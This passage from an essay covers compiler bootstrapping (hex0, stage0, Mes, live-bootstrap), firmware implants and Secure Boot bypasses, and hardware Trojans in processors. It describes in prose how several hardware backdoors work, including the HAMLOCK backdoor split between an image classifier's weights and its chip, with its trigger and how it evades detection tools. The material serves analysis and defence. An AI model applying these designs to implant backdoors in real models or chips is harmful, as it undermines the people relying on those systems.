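In hex0, `74` means "jump if the last two values compared were equal", and `14` is the distance, 20 bytes. The programmer has to count those bytes by hand, and recount them after inserting anything in between. In hex1, the programmer marks the destination with the letter `b`, and the tool works out the distance. The code changes to `0F84` because hex1 can only produce the longer form of the jump. Hex2 allows a descriptive name instead of a letter. M0 lets the programmer define `je` as another way of writing the digits, so the line contains no numbers.

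Up to this point the tools do little more than replace names with digits and work out distances, which a patient person could do on paper. A C compiler has to do much more, such as turning an expression like `c - 48` into a series of instructions. stage0, the collection of tools from hex0 to M2-Planet, splits this job between two compilers. The first, cc_x86, is written in assembly language and only has to compile the second, M2-Planet, so it can leave out every feature of C that M2-Planet does not use. M2-Planet then builds better versions of the earlier tools and finally itself.

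Mes, which came from a different project, consists of a Scheme interpreter and MesCC, a C compiler that runs on it. The interpreter is about 5,000 lines of simple C, which M2-Planet can compile. The first build of Mes compiles a second that is faster and has fewer bugs. Faase thinks Mes is more than this step requires. It is also slow, because the interpreter has to run the whole compiler and reload its Scheme files for every C file.

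MesCC can then compile a modified version of the Tiny C Compiler, the compiler Wheeler used in one of his DDC tests. The first copy lacks some features, such as support for numbers with fractions. In live-bootstrap, the compiler compiles its own source code three more times to gain these features, then builds the ordinary release.

### Climbing through old versions

The Tiny C Compiler cannot build a current version of GCC. Since version 4.8, released in 2013, GCC's own source code has required a C++ compiler. The developers of both projects therefore go back to versions written in C. Guix uses GCC 2.95.3 and works up to 4.9.4, with which it builds the rest of the system. Live-bootstrap goes through four versions:

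1. The Tiny C Compiler builds GCC 4.0.4.
2. GCC 4.0.4 builds GCC 4.7.4, the last version written in C, including its C++ compiler.
3. GCC 4.7.4 builds GCC 10.4, the last version that it can handle.
4. GCC 10.4 builds GCC 13.1.

Other programs also have to be built through a series of versions. Live-bootstrap builds seven versions of Perl and eight of Python, because each version comes with files that an earlier copy of the language generated.

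*live-bootstrap* (Štikonas, Dersey and fosslinux, 2020) treats those generated files as unsuitable for bootstrapping, even though they are text, because people cannot realistically audit them. Its rules exclude configuration scripts and parsers generated by other programs, as well as anything that a package downloads during its own build before it can be verified. It criticises Guix for accepting many such files. The rules make the project much slower to extend, but the XZ backdoor, which a build script activated, is a good argument for them.

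### The programs outside the seed

Guix's 357-byte seed, hex0, needs another program to start each build tool, give it the right files and store the results. In 2023 that program was a prebuilt copy of Guile, an implementation of Scheme, which at about 25 MiB was more than 70,000 times the size of hex0. Guile also ran the Scheme versions of the shell and utilities that Guix uses in the early steps. A corrupted Guile could alter the files that pass through it, so Guix still relied on unread binaries, though it had cut them by about nine tenths.

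Nieuwenhuizen and Timothy Sample were working to run the shell and utilities on Mes instead. Even if they succeeded, Guix would still use the ready-made Guile to direct the build, and in 2023 Nieuwenhuizen left open how to replace it.

The build also runs on an existing Linux kernel, which reads and writes every file involved. Rick Masters wrote builder-hex0 to remove this dependency. With it, live-bootstrap can start on a machine that has no operating system:

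1. The machine's firmware loads a small boot loader from the disk. Its hex0 listing has 209 lines, according to a change recorded on hacktivis.me.
2. The boot loader compiles a simple kernel, also written in hex0, and starts it. This listing ran to 2,442 lines when Stefanik (2024), in *Use builder-hex0 stages from submodule*, moved it to a separate project.
3. The simple kernel runs the stage0 tools, Mes and the Tiny C Compiler, which then builds a kernel called Fiwix.
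4. Fiwix takes over and runs the build as far as GCC 4.0.4 and Linux 4.14.
5. Linux takes over and builds everything else.

Fiwix is a clone of Linux 2.0 that is much easier to understand and compile than Linux. According to Fiwix (2024), its developer has accepted patches since October 2022 to let the Tiny C Compiler build it. In the first attempt to build Linux on Fiwix, Masters had to run live-bootstrap in phases because Fiwix kept rebooting for reasons he could not explain. He had also compiled Fiwix with an existing GCC, whereas the current process builds it from the seed.

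Live-bootstrap still needs a working computer to download the source code and arrange it on a disk, which the README calls "a currently unsolved problem". If that computer is corrupted, it could change the source code as it writes the disk. Live-bootstrap builds its own program for checking the files' checksums soon after building M2-Planet, but an attacker could also have changed the list of correct checksums if it came from the same computer. The defenders would need to compare the list with copies from elsewhere.

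### Comparing machines

The x86 version also relies on the BIOS or UEFI, the firmware that starts a PC. In LWN's *Comments on "Pulling Linux up by its bootstraps"* (2024), a reader using the name Phantom_Hoover argued that this leaves the whole structure "built on sand". The reader thought people already had better reasons to trust the binaries of GCC and Linux than to trust firmware, so making those binaries more trustworthy would add little security. Fosslinux, a live-bootstrap author, agreed that the firmware was very hard to trust, but was not convinced that it was much worse than ordinary software supply chains, which had proved more fragile than expected.

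Fosslinux also suggested running live-bootstrap on many different x86 machines and comparing the final checksums. As in DDC, a match means that either every machine is clean or all of them altered the result in the same way. Another reader sensibly proposed using processors from both Intel and AMD, firmware with different origins, different brands of disk drive and video adapter, and computers of very different ages.

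In 2019, people from the Reproducible Builds and Bootstrappable Builds projects made a smaller comparison of this kind. They built the Mes C compiler on three Linux distributions and got the same checksum each time, which is fairly strong evidence that none of the three toolchains had inserted code of its own into Mes.

### Progress by 2026

Guix's 2023 bootstrap worked only on x86 processors, and extending it to others was harder than it looked. GCC 2.95.3 is too old to support RISC-V, and the first GCC version that supports it needs a C++ compiler to build. Ekaitz Zarraga therefore added RISC-V support to an earlier version that doesn't need one. In June 2026 he described this work as "done" but "probably not great", according to Guix's *IRC channel logs* (2026).

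The same conversation also covers small kernels that a developer called alganet had built for other processors in the style of builder-hex0. They could start from the firmware and reach the first version of Mes on 32-bit and 64-bit x86, 64-bit ARM and RISC-V. The checksums of the stage0 tools matched, but alganet expected the new ARM and RISC-V kernels to be too slow and buggy for the later steps. Others had compiled the Tiny C Compiler on ARM and drafted a full ARM route for Nix. One of them thought the next realistic step was to adapt Fiwix. In mid-2026, the complete route from firmware to Linux still worked only on x86 machines, though many of the early steps worked on other processors.

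The early steps do not take long on a modern computer. A developer called siraben, working on an alternative route, estimated that it takes about 15 minutes to reach the Tiny C Compiler from a small Linux system, though the timed run he posted took 24. The middle of live-bootstrap is slower than it needs to be, because the build can use only one processor core until Linux starts.

### Languages that need their own route

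A clean GCC can build anything written in C or C++, but many other languages have self-hosting compilers. GNU's manual warns that some of these are "very hard or practically impossible to bootstrap", because they need a recent version of themselves to compile. Programs in those languages still run on a bootstrapped system, but they bring back the unread binaries the system was meant to avoid.

Rust's compiler is written in Rust, and each release needs the one before it, but the chain can be started with mrustc, a separate Rust compiler written in C++ that GCC can build. mrustc omits most checks for programmers' mistakes because it only has to compile programs already known to work. Flashner (2022), in *How long does it take to run the full rustc bootstrap chain?*, used it to build Rust 1.54 in about two hours on a 24-core machine. Each later version took another 30 to 45 minutes, so reaching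 version 1.60 took five to six and a half hours in total. Cournoyer (2022), replying to the same question, recalled that the chain had once taken 16 hours on a 12-core processor. The chain gets longer with every Rust release until mrustc is updated to compile a newer starting version.

Camlboot, a project by Nathanaëlle Courant, Julien Lepiller and Gabriel Scherer for the language OCaml, also adds a compiler of its own. The OCaml source code comes with a ready-made compiler binary, which builds the new compiler. Camlboot replaces that binary with two simpler programs: a compiler for a small part of OCaml, written in Scheme, and an interpreter for the full language, written in that small part. The interpreter runs the official compiler's source code directly, so the official compiler can compile itself without an existing binary.

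The researchers then used the result for DDC. They rebuilt the binary supplied with OCaml 4.07 and got an identical copy. If their own starting tools were clean, the supplied binary contained no trusting-trust attack. They had thus tested a compiler that other people had made and distributed, which Wheeler had been unable to do with Fedora's GCC. The test is also relevant to CompCert, whose proof does not cover the OCaml compiler that builds it.

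Haskell is harder to bootstrap because its main compiler, GHC, is written in Haskell and uses many of the language's more advanced features. A substitute compiler has to support many of those features to compile even an old version of GHC. Some early releases could be built from C code instead, but that code was generated by another copy of GHC, and live-bootstrap does not accept generated code of this kind. People who want a fully bootstrapped system may find it easier to do without programs written in Haskell.

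### How much source code is there to read?

A 357-byte seed can make people underestimate how much they have to trust. Hex0 only converts digits, so everything the finished system does comes from source code added later. An attacker who cannot hide a backdoor in the seed could try to hide one in that code.

The early tools are small enough for one person to read:

| Part | Size of the source code |
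|---|---|
| hex0, 64-bit version | 152 lines |
| builder-hex0's boot loader | 209 lines |
| builder-hex0's kernel | 2,442 lines |
| `mescc-tools`, the assemblers and other early utilities | 9,338 lines of C and 2,350 of assembly |
| Mes, interpreter only | About 5,000 lines of C |

The first and fourth figures come from the source-code archive that contains Debian's *hex0.hex0*. The total is about 19,500 lines, which would take roughly 100 hours to read at 200 lines an hour. The table leaves out M2-Planet and MesCC, and hex0 listings take longer to read than C, so several months is a safer estimate for everything up to the Tiny C Compiler.

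Later programs such as GCC and Linux are much larger, with millions of lines each. At the same speed, one person would need 25,000 hours, or about 14 working years, to read five million lines. The live-bootstrap project also takes more than 150 steps to reach GCC 10.4. No individual can check all this. A large group could, but it would miss a well-disguised flaw if it read at this speed.

The usual reply is that source code can at least be read. GNU's manual says that inspecting the programs in the chain "is a lot of work, but it can certainly be done." Source code is easier to inspect than 250 MB of binaries because people can divide it among themselves, search it, and discuss suspicious passages. They also have to read a fixed version only once, and anyone who doubts the result can read it again. But the XZ backdoor was publicly available for download, and nobody caught it by reading. Bootstrapping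 replaces an almost impossible inspection with a very long one that somebody still has to do.

The age of much of this code is partly an advantage, because an attacker who altered a twenty-year-old release today would have to replace every old copy in archives and on disks to hide the change. However, another reader on LWN pointed out that cryptographic checksums become less secure over time. If an old release was recorded only with a checksum that attackers have since learned to forge, a match no longer shows that the file is genuine. Live-bootstrap uses the newer SHA-256 checksums, but its developers could calculate them only from the copies they had.

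Old versions of GCC also contain known bugs, but these matter little, since each version only has to compile the next few programs. A deliberate flaw that targets those programs would be more serious. This made the reader who proposed testing on varied hardware uneasy about the fixed sequence of GCC versions. The reader suggested building through several different sequences of versions to check whether they produce the same final compiler, bit for bit. If a flaw in GCC 4.0.4 altered the final compiler, the result would differ from that of a sequence that skipped 4.0.4, unless the other sequence contained a matching flaw.

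## Can firmware be made trustworthy again?

Owners can rewrite some of a PC's firmware, and on certain older models they can replace most of it with code they built themselves. Many recent PCs prevent this by accepting only boot firmware that the maker has signed. Almost every PC also contains chips whose programs outsiders can't read.

Corrupted firmware could defeat even live-bootstrap, by changing its first program while loading it, after the defenders had checked every byte.

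### From the power button to the operating system

A PC contains several small computers besides its main processor, and some of them start first. On a typical Intel laptop, this is roughly what happens:

1. The embedded controller, a small chip that looks after the power button, keyboard and battery, turns on the power to the other chips.
2. The management processor starts. Intel calls its version the Management Engine, and AMD has a similar one. Its first instructions come from a boot ROM, permanent memory inside the chip, and the rest from a flash chip on the motherboard.
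3. The main processor starts UEFI, the successor to the BIOS, from the same flash chip. UEFI sets up the memory and finds the other devices. Schneier (2022), in *New UEFI Rootkit*, quotes a description of it as an operating system "in its own right".
4. UEFI puts system management code in a part of memory that the operating system can't see. Certain events, such as a hardware fault, make the processor stop what it is doing and run this code.
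5. UEFI loads a boot loader from a small partition of the disk. If a feature called Secure Boot is on, UEFI first checks the boot loader's signature. On Linux, according to The Hacker News' *11 Old Microsoft-Signed Linux UEFI Shims Could Let Attackers Bypass Secure Boot* (2026), UEFI checks a small program called a shim, the shim checks the main boot loader, and the boot loader checks the kernel.
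6. The kernel takes over. The management processor, disk and network card go on running their own firmware.

Most servers also have a baseboard management controller, a separate computer that lets administrators operate the machine remotely. It can restart the server, attach virtual disks and rewrite firmware, according to Help Net Security's *Exposed BMCs hand out password hashes before login* (2026).

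| Firmware | Can it read or alter a freshly rebuilt system? |
|---|---|
| Boot ROM | Indirectly, because it decides what runs next |
| UEFI | Yes, while it loads the system |
| System management code | Yes, at any time on most PCs |
| Management processor | Yes on many PCs, because it has its own route to memory |
| Embedded controller | Usually not, but it sees every key typed on a laptop |
| Disk controller | It can alter any file on its way to memory, and many newer drives can reach memory directly |
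| Network card | Yes, unless the system restricts it |
| Server management controller | Yes, for example by starting the server from a virtual disk |

A circuit called an IOMMU can limit which parts of memory a disk or network card can access. The operating system has to switch it on and gets the list of devices it covers from UEFI, so corrupted UEFI could leave a device off that list.

### Implants that survived a clean installation

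| Implant | What the attackers altered | What it could survive |
|---|---|---|
| Equation Group's module (2015) | Firmware of hard drives | Erasing the drive and reinstalling the operating system |
| LoJax (2018) | UEFI, by adding a module | Reinstalling Windows and replacing the drive |
| MoonBounce (2022) | UEFI, by changing an existing part | Formatting or replacing the drive |
| BlackLotus (2023) | The boot loader on the disk | All Windows updates available at the time |
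| BlackX (2026) | The boot loader on the disk | Windows updates, and reinstalling Windows if the boot partition stays the same |

Kaspersky (2015) described the tools of a team of hackers called the Equation Group. One module could reprogram the firmware of 12 categories of hard drive. It also gave other malicious programs access to hidden storage on the drive, according to the report quoted in bit-tech's *Kaspersky outs hard drive infecting malware*. Kaspersky thought the group had probably used the module only a few times, because each model of drive would take months of work and millions in investment. That would no longer be reassuring if skilled work became cheap.

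LoJax imitated LoJack, a legitimate anti-theft program that many laptop makers put in their firmware so that a thief can't remove it by reinstalling Windows. ESET's *LoJax* (2018) confirmed at least one successful installation in firmware. The campaign mostly targeted government bodies in the Balkans and Central and Eastern Europe.

MoonBounce was harder to notice because it changed an existing component of UEFI and left nothing on the hard drive. Kaspersky found it on a single machine, using a firmware scanner built into its security software. Such a scanner runs on the computer it is examining, so it can detect only implants that don't falsify what it reads. According to a Kaspersky statement carried by Zawya, another UEFI implant, CosmicStrand, seems to have been in use from the end of 2016, well before anyone publicly described such attacks. As with compilers, the known cases may not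 be representative of those still undiscovered.

LoJax and MoonBounce both worked by inserting programs into Windows. They would probably not have affected a bootstrapped Linux system or the tiny kernels of live-bootstrap. But an attacker who controls UEFI and knows what the defenders plan to run could write an implant for it.

BlackLotus and BlackX are easier to remove, because formatting the whole disk normally deletes them. They matter more for what they revealed about Secure Boot. ESET (2023) found that BlackLotus, which criminals could buy for $5,000, worked on fully updated Windows 11 machines. It included old Microsoft boot programs with a flaw that Microsoft had fixed in newer versions, but PCs still accepted Microsoft's signature on the old ones.

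Three years later, Kaspersky found BlackX using the same flaw against diplomatic organisations in Central Asia. By then Microsoft offered a way to make PCs reject the old programs, but administrators had to turn it on by hand, and few did, according to Infobae's *Un software espía infectó equipos con Windows que tenían todas las actualizaciones* (2026). The old certificate expired in October 2026, but PCs still accept programs signed with it until somebody adds the certificate to their list of banned signatures.

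Secure Boot therefore trusts every program that Microsoft has ever signed, apart from those on the list. In July ESET (2026) reported 11 more old shims that attackers could use to bypass Secure Boot, even on machines that had never had the software the shims came from. Microsoft had banned all 11 in its June updates. Many PCs let owners replace Microsoft's certificates with their own, so that Secure Boot no longer trusts the programs Microsoft has signed. However, some graphics and network cards may then stop working, because only Microsoft's certificates cover their start-up code.

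### New flaws in UEFI and servers

Attackers can choose from many flaws to install new implants. The security company Binarly (2026) keeps a collection of 80,000 UEFI images and found at least one serious vulnerability in 98 percent of the firmware released in 2025. PurePC's *Hakerzy mogą zainfekować płyty główne serwerów Supermicro nieusuwalnymi wirusami* reports that Binarly also discovered flaws in Supermicro's server boards that year, which would let malicious firmware pass the signature check and survive a complete wipe of the disks.

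In 2026 HD Moore of the security company runZero presented 123 vulnerabilities in server management controllers from eight manufacturers. Some let an attacker without a password run programs on the server itself, according to Kerner's *Out of band, out of mind*. TechRadar's *Buggy microcontrollers making up some of the world's most important servers* reports that about 86,000 of these controllers were reachable from the public internet. Although vulnerable, most of these machines may contain no implant. But somebody who restores the manufacturer's firmware after an attack may also restore the flaw that let the attacker in.

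### Rewriting the flash chip from outside

Software running on a PC has to read the flash chip through the PC's own hardware and firmware. A flash programmer, a small device with a clip that fits over the chip's pins, bypasses both. The owner turns the PC off, disconnects the battery, reads the chip through the clip, writes a clean image and reads it back to check it. This removes an implant like LoJax or MoonBounce. In TechByte (2018), ESET advises owners who can't do this to replace the motherboard.

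Detecting an implant is harder than removing it. The chip stores settings, serial numbers and logs alongside the firmware, so its contents never match the maker's published image exactly, and somebody has to explain each difference. The owner should save a copy before overwriting anything, since it may be the only evidence of an attack.

The clip reaches only one chip, and the embedded controller, disk and network card may store their firmware elsewhere, often inside a chip with no pins for reading it. Kaspersky points out that the usual commands for checking or replacing a drive's firmware go through that same firmware, so a corrupted drive can return false results. It advises throwing away a suspect drive and buying a new one, but the owner can't check that the new drive is clean either.

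### Open firmware

A clean copy of the maker's firmware is still millions of bytes that the owner can't read. Three projects offer code that people can read and build themselves:

- **coreboot** replaces most of UEFI. It sets up the hardware and then hands over to another program, which loads the operating system.
- **Heads** adds a small Linux system to coreboot. It checks the files on the boot partition against a signature made with the owner's key, which replaces Microsoft's.
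- **oreboot** is a version of coreboot written in Rust instead of C. It aims to include no ready-made binaries, but it supports only a few boards, mostly with RISC-V processors.

Defenders could bootstrap GCC from hex0, use it to build coreboot, and compare the result with other people's builds. To build oreboot from the same seed, they would also have to work through the long chain of Rust compilers.

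The main limit is hardware support. Processor makers don't fully publish the details needed to set up the memory of a recent PC, so on most recent Intel machines coreboot has to run a binary from Intel for this step, before any operating system starts.

Open firmware can also contain serious flaws. Most PC makers base their UEFI firmware on EDK II, an open-source project. In 2026 researchers at Anthropic and Google found a remotely exploitable flaw in it, rated 9.5 out of 10 for severity, according to TechRadar's *Most data centers and servers on the planet could be vulnerable*. No attacks were known, but each maker has to fix its own version, which could take months. Owners of a supported coreboot machine can rebuild their firmware with a fix the same day.

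### Measured boot

Secure Boot tries to stop unapproved programs from running. Measured boot lets them run but records them in a security chip called a TPM. Each program calculates a checksum of the next one and sends it to the TPM before starting it. The TPM keeps a running value, R, which starts at zero and changes with each checksum:

```
new R = SHA-256(old R followed by the checksum)
```

With UEFI, a boot loader and a kernel, this happens three times. If the boot loader changes by one bit, its checksum changes, and so does the final R. A malicious boot loader can send more checksums afterwards, but it has no practical way to find one that restores R to the expected value.

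The TPM can be set to release a secret only when R is correct. Windows can use this for BitLocker, its disk encryption. According to ESET, the BlackLotus installer got around this check by switching off BitLocker's protection before restarting the PC, because otherwise the PC would have shown a recovery screen and alerted the victim. Heads can use the secret to calculate a six-digit code, which the owner compares with one on a phone.

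All this relies on the first program in the chain, which nothing has measured. An attacker who replaces the part of UEFI that takes the first measurement can make it send the checksum of the clean UEFI, and every later value will be correct. The TPM will then release the secret, and Heads will show the right code. Some PCs avoid this by making the processor measure the start of UEFI, but the owner then has to trust the processor maker's code instead. On many recent PCs, the TPM is also a program on the management processor.

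### Keys that the owner cannot change

Intel's Boot Guard is meant to protect the first step. It works as follows:

1. In the factory, the laptop maker burns the checksum of its public key into fuses in the chipset or processor. Each fuse can change only once.
2. At every start, the processor runs a small program signed by Intel. It reads the maker's public key from the flash chip and compares its checksum with the fuses.
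3. It uses this key to check the maker's signature on a list of checksums.
4. It compares the first part of UEFI with that list. If anything is wrong, the strictest setting stops the PC from starting.

The PC now won't start if an attacker alters the protected part of the flash chip or if the owner installs coreboot, because neither has the maker's private key to sign the new code. Rewriting the flash chip doesn't remove this restriction, because the fuses aren't on that chip. AMD has a similar feature. In 2022 Kaspersky described protections of this kind as "gradually being adopted".

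For most people this is probably a good exchange, since they are more likely to face a firmware attack than to write firmware. It is worse for defenders whose adversary may have the maker's key. After a break-in at the computer maker MSI in 2023, criminals published private keys for Boot Guard. Anyone with such a key can sign an implant that the matching PCs will accept, and the owners can't burn new fuses to reject it. Nor can the owners replace the maker's code, however many flaws it has. Defenders can avoid the problem by choosing PCs from before 2013, when Intel introduced Boot Guard, or from one of the few makers that leave the fuses unset.

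### The programmer is a computer too

A cheap flash programmer contains its own chip and plugs into another computer, which supplies the clean image and displays the result of the comparison. If that computer is compromised, it could write an implant to the flash chip and still report a match.

Defenders can read the firmware with several unrelated chip programmers and computers and compare the results, much as in DDC. They can also build a chip programmer from a simple microcontroller whose whole program is short enough for a person to read.

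A person could in principle check part of the flash chip without a computer, by sending read commands with switches and reading the data from a light. On common flash chips, reading one byte takes 40 pulses: 8 for the instruction, 24 for the address and 8 for the data. At one pulse a second, checking 1,000 randomly chosen bytes would take about 11 hours. If an implant had changed 50,000 of the 16,777,216 bytes on a 16 MB chip, the chance of missing all of them would be (1 − 50,000/16,777,216)^1000, or about 5 percent. For an implant of 500 bytes, it would be about 97 percent, so this method works only against large changes. The check also requires a clean image for comparison. The chip could even contain circuitry that returns false data, which no test of its contents can rule out.

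### How much unreadable firmware remains?

When owners can't replace a piece of firmware, they may be able to remove the part that runs it. They can take out a Wi-Fi card or use a server board without a management controller. The management processor is harder to avoid, because recent Intel PCs won't run normally without it. On some models, owners can delete most of its firmware or set a switch meant to stop it after start-up, but the processor still has to run first, and the switch relies on the processor to stop itself. On a few laptops from around 2008, such as the ThinkPad X200, owners can delete all of its firmware.

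The table compares a typical recent laptop with a ThinkPad X230, a 2012 model that runs coreboot and Heads, and an ATmega328P, a microcontroller popular with hobbyists.

| Firmware | Recent laptop | ThinkPad X230 with coreboot | ATmega328P |
|---|---|---|---|
| Main boot firmware | Mostly closed, on a chip of 16 to 32 MB | Open, built from source | None, apart from the owner's program of up to 32 KB |
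| Management processor | Several MB | About 100 KB after deletions | None |
| Processor microcode | Closed | Closed | None |
| Embedded controller | Closed | Closed | None |
| Disk and Wi-Fi | Closed | Closed, but the owner can remove both | None |

At five seconds a byte, reading everything on a full 32 MB chip once would take about 26 working years. Reading the 100 KB on the X230 would take three and a half working weeks, although understanding it would take much longer. The ATmega328P has no such firmware to read, but its 2 KB of working memory is far too little for a C compiler. It is enough for a program like hex0 or for reading a flash chip.

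## Can a chip be checked, or replaced by one that can?

Nobody can fully check a modern processor and then use it. Imaging individual transistors usually destroys the chip, and some alterations don't show up even then. People can choose simpler chips, or chips they configure themselves, but the examples below run at clock speeds 40 to 200,000 times lower than a 4 GHz PC.

A hardware Trojan is a malicious change to a chip's circuitry. It can undo all the work described so far, because a corrupted processor can run a clean binary incorrectly.

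### Where an attacker can alter a chip

An engineer describes a circuit in source code, using a language such as Verilog. Design software translates this code into standard cells, small ready-made circuits from the chip factory's library, and lays out the cells and the wires between them. The factory turns the resulting layout file into masks, the stencils it uses to print each layer onto silicon.

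| Stage | What an attacker could alter | Which chips carry the change |
|---|---|---|
| Design files | The source code, or a block bought from another company | All of them |
| Design software | The circuit it produces from clean source code | All chips designed with that copy |
| Masks | One or more layers of the layout | All chips made with those masks |
| Factory | The masks, or the chemical treatment of the silicon | Whole batches, or selected wafers |
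| Packaging and shipping | The whole chip, by swapping it for another | As few as one |

The last stage is easy to underestimate. Huang once dissolved the plastic around several memory cards sold under the same brand and product name, and found that the chips inside varied widely (*Infra-Red, In-Situ (IRIS) Inspection of Silicon*, 2023).

Chip design software poses the same problem as a compiler. It translates source code into something that people can hardly read, so a corrupted copy could recognise a processor and add a backdoor, much as Thompson's compiler recognised the login program. The design software is also a binary that some compiler built, and it runs on a processor that earlier design software laid out. In principle, an implant could pass from software to chip and back again, though there is no known example. Defenders can apply DDC or bootstrapping to open-source design software,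 but not to most commercial design software, because its source code is secret.

### From a thousand extra gates to none

In 2008 King, Tucek and colleagues, in *Designing and implementing malicious hardware*, presented the Illinois Malicious Processor, an altered version of the open-source processor Leon3. Its login backdoor works as follows:

1. The attacker sends the computer an unrequested network packet. The operating system has to examine the packet before discarding it, so the bytes pass through the processor.
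2. An added circuit recognises a sequence in those bytes. It loads the rest of the packet as a hidden program into a reserved part of the cache, the processor's own fast memory.
3. The hidden program watches the login program. When somebody types "letmein", it makes the password check succeed.
4. After the login, it removes itself.

The login backdoor took 117 lines of source code and added 1,341 logic gates to the original 1,787,958, an increase of 0.08 percent. A smaller version with 959 extra gates let any program read and change all of the computer's memory. The login backdoor has a similar effect to Thompson's attack, but it leaves the login program's binary clean, so checking that binary would not reveal the backdoor.

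Leaving the backdoor on slowed the computer by 13 percent on average. When it was on only for the attack, the slowdown was 1.34 percent, almost the same as the 1.32 percent when the attacker logged in with the real password and stole the same file.

Ordinary testing is unlikely to find such a circuit. King and colleagues consider a processor with 16 registers of 32 bits, a 16 KB instruction cache and a 64 KB data cache. Together these hold 512 + 131,072 + 524,288 = 655,872 bits, so the processor has at least 2^655,872 possible states. A tester can try only a tiny fraction of these states, and the attacker needs just one as the trigger.

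*Stealthy Dopant-Level Hardware Trojans* (Becker, Regazzoni and colleagues, 2013) altered circuits without adding gates, by changing the dopants, the impurities that determine how each part of a transistor conducts. An inverter, for example, normally turns a 0 into a 1 and a 1 into a 0. One of its transistors connects the output to the power supply, and the other connects it to ground. With the wrong dopants, the first connection becomes permanent and the second stops working, so the inverter always outputs 1. The wires and the shapes of the transistors stay the same.

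They applied this to a random number generator based on the one in Intel's Ivy Bridge processors. Its last stage encrypts a 128-bit value with a 128-bit key, both of which should be unpredictable. The Trojan fixes the whole key and all but 32 bits of the value, which leaves only 2^32, or about 4.3 billion, possible outputs. The output still passes a standard set of statistical tests because encryption makes it look random. An attacker who knows the fixed bits and tries a million possibilities a second would need at most 72 minutes to find the right one. The generator's built-in self-test compares a checksum with a stored one, but the attacker can choose fixed bits that give the expected checksum.

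Their second Trojan alters two gates in an encryption circuit so that one combination of inputs uses nearly twice as much energy, but the outputs stay the same. Someone who measures the chip's power consumption can then work out the secret key.

A2, a hardware Trojan that researchers at the University of Michigan presented in 2016, needs an added circuit only about as large as a single standard cell. The circuit contains a capacitor, which stores a little charge each time a chosen wire switches on or off. In normal use the wire rarely switches, so the charge leaks away. A malicious program can make the wire switch repeatedly until the capacitor fills up, which flips the bit that records whether a program has full control of the processor. Digital tests check for wrong outputs, so they don't detect the charge building up. The researchers had a chip manufactured with the Trojan in it, and the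 Trojan worked. As a defence, *T-TER* (2019) proposes tamper-evident routing, which lays out important wires so that an attacker can't connect to them without leaving signs.

Becker and colleagues wrote in 2013 that nobody had found a real hardware Trojan, and that all the examples came from universities. As with compilers, this is only weak evidence that none exist, since few people look inside their chips.

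### A backdoor split between a model and its chip

An ordinary backdoor in an AI model sits entirely in the weights, where inspection tools may find it. *HAMLOCK* (Amgain, Lobo and colleagues, 2025) describes a backdoor split between the weights and the chip that runs the model. The paper tests it on image classifiers, with a small square in the picture as the trigger.

The attacker changes the weights of up to three neurons, the model's basic computing units, so that the square makes them produce unusually large numbers. The model still classifies the image correctly. The chip contains one circuit that monitors those neurons and another that changes the answer.

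The first circuit can be tiny because of how computers store numbers. A common 32-bit format uses one bit for the sign, eight for the exponent and 23 for the remaining digits. If the stored exponent is `e`, the number's size is at least 2^(e − 127) and less than twice that. A neuron's output of 3 has `e` = 128, and an output of 1,000 has `e` = 136. A circuit that checks whether `e` is greater than 133 detects every positive output of 128 or more from just eight bits. The second circuit raises the exponent of the score for the attacker's chosen answer. Adding 4, for instance, multiplies the score by 16.

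On the corrupted chip, the simplest version of the backdoor made the model misclassify every image that contained the square, according to Help Net Security's *A hardware neural network backdoor that hides in plain sight*. A version that used several neurons succeeded about 95 percent of the time. Without the chip, the model gave the attacker's answer for less than 1 percent of these images. Two tools for detecting tampered models found nothing, because they look for a trigger that causes wrong answers, and the square causes none without the chip. Retraining didn't remove the backdoor. In one run the defenders had real examples of the attack, but the model already classified them correctly, so retraining on them reinforced its response to the square.

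The circuits added at most about 0.1 percent to the chip's area. Amgain and colleagues call the Trojan undetectable, but they designed the circuits in software and did not manufacture a chip or run hardware tests. Electron microscope images would probably show the extra gates to anyone with a clean design for comparison. But the company designing the chip may be the attacker, in which case the owner has no clean design. One of the researchers, Swarup Bhunia, told Help Net Security that he expects the method to work on chips that run language models, and that his group is working on this. He suggests monitoring a model's internal behaviour while it runs, which might detect the attack without an image of the chip.

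### Comparing a chip with its design

*Red Team vs. Blue Team*, by Puschner, Moos and colleagues, reports the most informative public test of chip inspection, from 2023. It compared four real chips with their design files. One team introduced differences, and another tried to find them without knowing where they were. The chips had already been made, so the first team altered the design files instead, according to Ruhr University Bochum's *Detecting manipulations in microchips*. This works because the comparison is the same whether the chip or the file has changed.

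The second team ground and etched away the silicon from the back of each chip until the lowest layer was visible. They took several thousand pictures with an electron microscope, joined them together and lined them up with the design. A program then compared each cell with a reference picture of the same type of cell. It also searched for circuits where the design had only filler cells, which take up unused space.

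| Size of the smallest features | Cells on the chip | Added cells found | Replaced cells found | False alarms | Imaging time |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 90 nm | 453,850 | 4 of 4 | 6 of 6 | 136 | 34 hours |
| 65 nm | 571,060 | 4 of 4 | 6 of 6 | 6 | 23 hours |
| 40 nm | 917,819 | 4 of 4 | 6 of 6 | 15 | 53 hours |
| 28 nm | 1,467,851 | 4 of 4 | 3 of 6 | 360 | 36 hours |

The team found 37 of the 40 changes. A person has to examine each of the 517 false alarms, but that is a manageable number among 3.4 million cells. Dust or debris obscured 161 cells, so a cleaner room would help.

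Puschner and colleagues report how many hours their checks took, but not how much they cost. The comparison took a computer only two to five hours per chip. They examined only 1 to 2 square millimetres of each chip, so imaging would be the bottleneck for a larger one. At the rate for the 28 nm chip, imaging a processor of 100 square millimetres would take about 3,700 hours, or five months of continuous work. Microscopes designed for chips could be faster. King and colleagues cite a figure from 2000 of up to a week and $250,000 for recovering a chip's complete circuit diagram, which is harder than comparing the chip with a known design.

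### Different cells that look the same

The first team put its changes in random places, but a real attacker would choose replacements that are hard to see. *Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions* (Dorschel, Walendy and colleagues, 2026) looks for such replacements in the same images.

They compared the positions of the vias, tiny vertical connections that show up as bright dots. The similarity score of two cells is the share of dots that match, so 12 matches out of 16 give 0.75, and identical patterns score 1. At 28 nm, five pairs of cells with different functions scored 1. Most of the very similar pairs were opposites, such as XOR, which outputs 1 when its two inputs differ, and XNOR, which outputs 1 when they are the same.

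The new method found all 24 replaced cells in the 2023 test, including the three the original team had missed. But at 65 nm it raised more than 5,000 false alarms, because it mistook bright spots in the images for vias. No method based on vias can distinguish cells with identical via patterns, however good the images are.

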